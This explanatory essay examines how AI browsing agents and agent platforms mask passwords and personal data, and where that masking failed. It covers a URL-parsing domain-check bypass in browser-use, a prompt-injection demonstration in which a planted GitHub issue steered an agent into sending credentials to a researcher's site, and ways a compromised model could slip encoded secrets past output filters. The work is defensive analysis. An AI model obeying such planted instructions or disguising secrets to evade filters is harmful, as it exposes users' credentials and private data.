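The domain limit could be bypassed. Before each visit, the code compared the site's domain with the user's list. But a web address can contain login details before the domain, and the code mistook part of these for the domain. An address that seemed to match the list could therefore lead somewhere else, including to services on a company's internal network. Mudryi, Chaklosh and Wójcik found the fault, now known as CVE-2025-47241, while reading the source code (*The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents*, 2025). GitHub Advisory Database's *GHSA-x39x-9qw5-ghrf*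 (2025) rates its severity 9.3 out of 10 and lists version 0.1.45, released on 3 May 2025, as the fix.

This broke the condition that the trusted code is correct. The fault was in the check on where the agent could take the password, not in the masking. The model still hadn't read the password, and the table was unchanged. Mudryi and colleagues found no sign that the code handling secrets consulted the domain list, so if the agent reached the wrong page, nothing further would have stopped the code from typing the password there.

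They also built an attack that didn't need the hole. They gave an agent running on GPT-4o a username and password, set no domain limit to tie the password to its proper site, and told the agent to read the issues posted on a GitHub project. One issue contained planted instructions to collect the placeholders and submit them on the researchers' own website. Since browser-use replaces any placeholder in an action with the real value before carrying it out, the website would receive the actual login. This is the same kind of attack as the supplier's email in the previous section, carried out against a popular product.

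Mudryi and colleagues report a working demonstration but no success rate. They suspect that placing the page's text at the end of the prompt helped the attack. Watson and colleagues also thought instructions had more influence there. Later versions of the system let the user tie each secret to a domain.

### Text that went around the masker

A second fault let real values reach the model. Browser-use keeps a history of what each action returned and includes it in later messages to the model. According to Aikido (2025), a security company, versions 0.7.8 to 0.11.0 didn't filter this history, so the model could read any password or access key that an action returned. If a user had listed an access key as secret and the agent opened the settings page that displays it, the full key would have gone to the model's provider.

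Masking failed here because not every input passed through the masker. Even with a secure table and flawless substitution code, the model would still have received the value by another path. Aikido doesn't list versions before 0.7.8 as affected, so an update probably introduced the gap. It lasted from 17 September to 12 December 2025, through 17 full releases.

It is less reassuring, then, that a programmer can read the substitution code in an afternoon, because reading it wouldn't have revealed this fault. The programmer would have had to find every place where the library adds text to a message, and check again after each release. Masking the finished request just before it leaves, as Agyemang and colleagues' proxy does, is safer because a new kind of message can't then skip the masking by accident.

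Microsoft's Playwright MCP, another tool that gives AI agents a browser, had a similar gap. According to Bug0's *Playwright MCP and CLI now redact secrets from console logs*, the redaction users had configured didn't apply to console messages, which a page's scripts write mainly for developers. Microsoft closed the gap in late June 2026.

Even when the model receives only placeholders, the secret values can end up in saved files. Browser Use warns that a saved run contains placeholders for the secrets the agent typed, but that its page snapshots and results are not redacted. Someone who opens the file may find a password in a snapshot.

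### When the model writes the code

In version 1.0 of browser-use, released on 10 November 2026, the model writes Python code that the library runs, instead of choosing from a list of actions as it did before. To log in, the model's code calls `type_secret('password')`, and the library types the value.

The destination check has improved. If the user has tied a secret to a domain, the library uses the browser, rather than the page's own scripts, to identify the page that will receive the keystrokes, and types nothing if it can't identify it. But the secret values now sit in the same process as the model's code, and Browser Use states that this code can read them. A compromised model can therefore use its code to read $S$, so the confidentiality claim no longer holds for such a model.

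The company seems to have accepted this in return for a more capable agent. Browser Use (2026) reported its highest accuracy yet when it made a similar change to its command-line tool in July.

To keep secrets out of the model's context, version 1.0 searches whatever the code returns and replaces any secret it finds with a label. It looks for each secret as typed and in several common altered forms, such as reversed, in capitals, or encoded in base64 or hexadecimal. This should catch most accidental leaks. It doesn't cover screenshots or files that the model's code writes, and a compromised model can write code that puts a secret in a form the search doesn't check for.

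Zunic (2026), in *browser-use 1.0.8*, calls the domain limit "a guard for an aligned model, not a sandbox". A permitted page can still load images from other hosts, and OpenAI also describes image loading as a way for private data to leave unnoticed. Python code run by the model can also open its own network connections. Zunic recommends running untrusted tasks in a container or a virtual machine. That would protect the user's other files, but not a password the user has put inside for the agent to use.

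### Masking the input and filtering the output

Build servers, which compile, test and publish software, had this problem before language models did. Their scripts need passwords and keys, so the server searches each build's log for the ones it knows and replaces them with asterisks. Because the scripts hold the real keys, a script can get one past the search by printing it in another form. In March 2025, attackers altered tj-actions/changed-files, a widely used build component, so that it wrote builds' secrets into their logs in encoded form.

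Sim, an open-source platform for running AI workflows, also searches for exact values rather than patterns, which it can do because its code fetches each secret. It replaces the secret with the name of its variable, so that an engineer can still tell which key was involved in an error. Sim's developers acknowledge that this method has limits. An encoded copy of a secret no longer contains the original characters, and a few lines of code can print a key one character at a time without any single output matching it. No general method can decide whether an arbitrary program will do this. Sim therefore also records which secrets each run used, so that misuse leaves a record even when the filter misses it.

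Sim replaces only values of at least eight characters, because shorter ones turn up too often in ordinary text. It would replace Keller's number, 555-0142, which has exactly eight characters, but leave her six-letter surname readable. The limit is reasonable for access keys, which are long, but would work poorly for personal details.

The same exact-match search gives much stronger protection on the model's input than on its output. Keller has no reason to disguise her phone number, so an input search only has to handle accidental variations in how she writes it. An output search checks text written by a model that already has the number and may be trying to leak it in a disguised form.

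Output filters are still useful against mistakes. AWS, Amazon's cloud business, recommends masking most personal details in an agent's output and blocking credentials altogether. It also recommends passing every output through the same filter, including outputs that users never see. This would catch a phone number that an uncompromised model repeats by mistake. It wouldn't hide the number from the model's provider, which received it with the prompt, or stop a compromised model from encoding the number in ordinary words.

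The masking has to happen before the untrusted component sees the value. This is practical for passwords, because an agent can log in without knowing them. Browserless' *Changelog/July 2026* (2026) announced a design in which the company's server fetches the password from the user's 1Password vault, types it in, and then locks the session so that the agent can't take a screenshot of the field or read it back. In 1Password's version for Claude, the agent receives a description of the login and is told whether it worked, and a person approves every release of a credential.

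Those are the companies' own descriptions, not results of attacks on the finished products. They do address the routes that caused trouble in browser-use, which were screenshots, returned text and code that can read the secret. Password managers also make destination rules easier to set up, because each saved login already includes its website. Browser Use's hosted service uses that stored website to decide where the agent may enter a password. Nobody has to write a new rule, but this works only for values with one obvious destination.

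### Why Salesforce switched masking off

Salesforce sells the masking layer described at the start, but its *LLM Data Masking* reports that the company disabled masking for Agentforce, its platform for AI agents, while keeping it for simpler features such as suggested replies to customers. The document gives three reasons: masking adds delay, it interferes with the agent's planning and actions, and many customers reported less accurate answers.

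Salesforce relies on other protections instead, and they don't all address the same attacker:

| Protection | Against a provider that keeps or misuses prompts | Against instructions planted in a record |
|---|---|---|
| Agreement that the provider keeps no data | Helps if the provider honours it | No effect |
| Access controls and limits on the agent's actions | Fewer records reach the provider | A hijacked agent can reach and do less |
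| Model hosted inside Salesforce's own network (planned) | Data stays within that network | No effect |
| Masking | Provider gets placeholders for whatever the detector found | A hijacked agent can't read masked values, but can misuse placeholders |

A company worried mainly about its model provider may do better to host the model itself than to mask data, because self-hosting also protects details that a detector would miss. Self-hosting offers less protection against planted instructions. If an Agentforce agent needs a customer's record to do its job, the access controls let it read that record, and someone who hijacks the agent can use everything in the record.

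The complaint about delay is hard to reconcile with the measurements. In the résumé test, even the slowest detector added less than 1% to the wait. An agent that calls the model twenty times masks text and waits for the model twenty times, so the proportion stays about the same. Long records would take longer to search, and a masker built on a language model can be very slow, as Grötzner and Tippe's gateway was. Salesforce says its masking searches for patterns and for database fields marked as sensitive, which should be fast. It gives no figures, so the delay may come from another part of its system.

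The complaint about planning is stronger, because masking itself causes the problem and a better placeholder wouldn't help. Salesforce gives the example of an agent that looks up a customer account and lists similar ones. If the record shows only that [COMPANY_1] is in [CITY_1], the agent can't tell which other cities are nearby. Browser Use points out that a model also can't adapt or split a value it never sees, such as a date it has to enter through a calendar, though this is a smaller problem.

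Code can take over some of this work. The model could call a tool to find accounts near [CITY_1], and the tool would look up the real city and run the search. A programmer could also store the day, month and year of a date separately. But somebody has to anticipate each operation, which is a problem for an agent bought to handle unexpected requests. The tool's results may also reveal the city.

Some of the lost accuracy may have come from the choice of placeholders. Salesforce writes that its masking inserted "fictional but realistic approximations", although its training material shows labels such as `<Person_0>`. In Ma and colleagues' tests, invented values made agents much less helpful than type labels did. Invented names are particularly bad for agents that look up records, because the search finds nobody, or the wrong customer, unless code first restores the real name. If Agentforce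 used invented values, labels might have recovered a good part of the lost accuracy. Salesforce reports no trial of both kinds of placeholder on the same tasks, which would settle this.

An agent also doesn't need every detail it receives. Brave's *Privacy risks of agentic oversharing on the Web* gives the example of an agent that is shopping for glucose tests and reveals that its user is divorced, through what it types or which options it clicks. Hiding the divorce from that agent would not make it less accurate. The agent comparing customer accounts may need the city and the industry, but probably not the contact's phone number. Salesforce's masking can already work field by field, so it could have masked the phone number and left the city readable.
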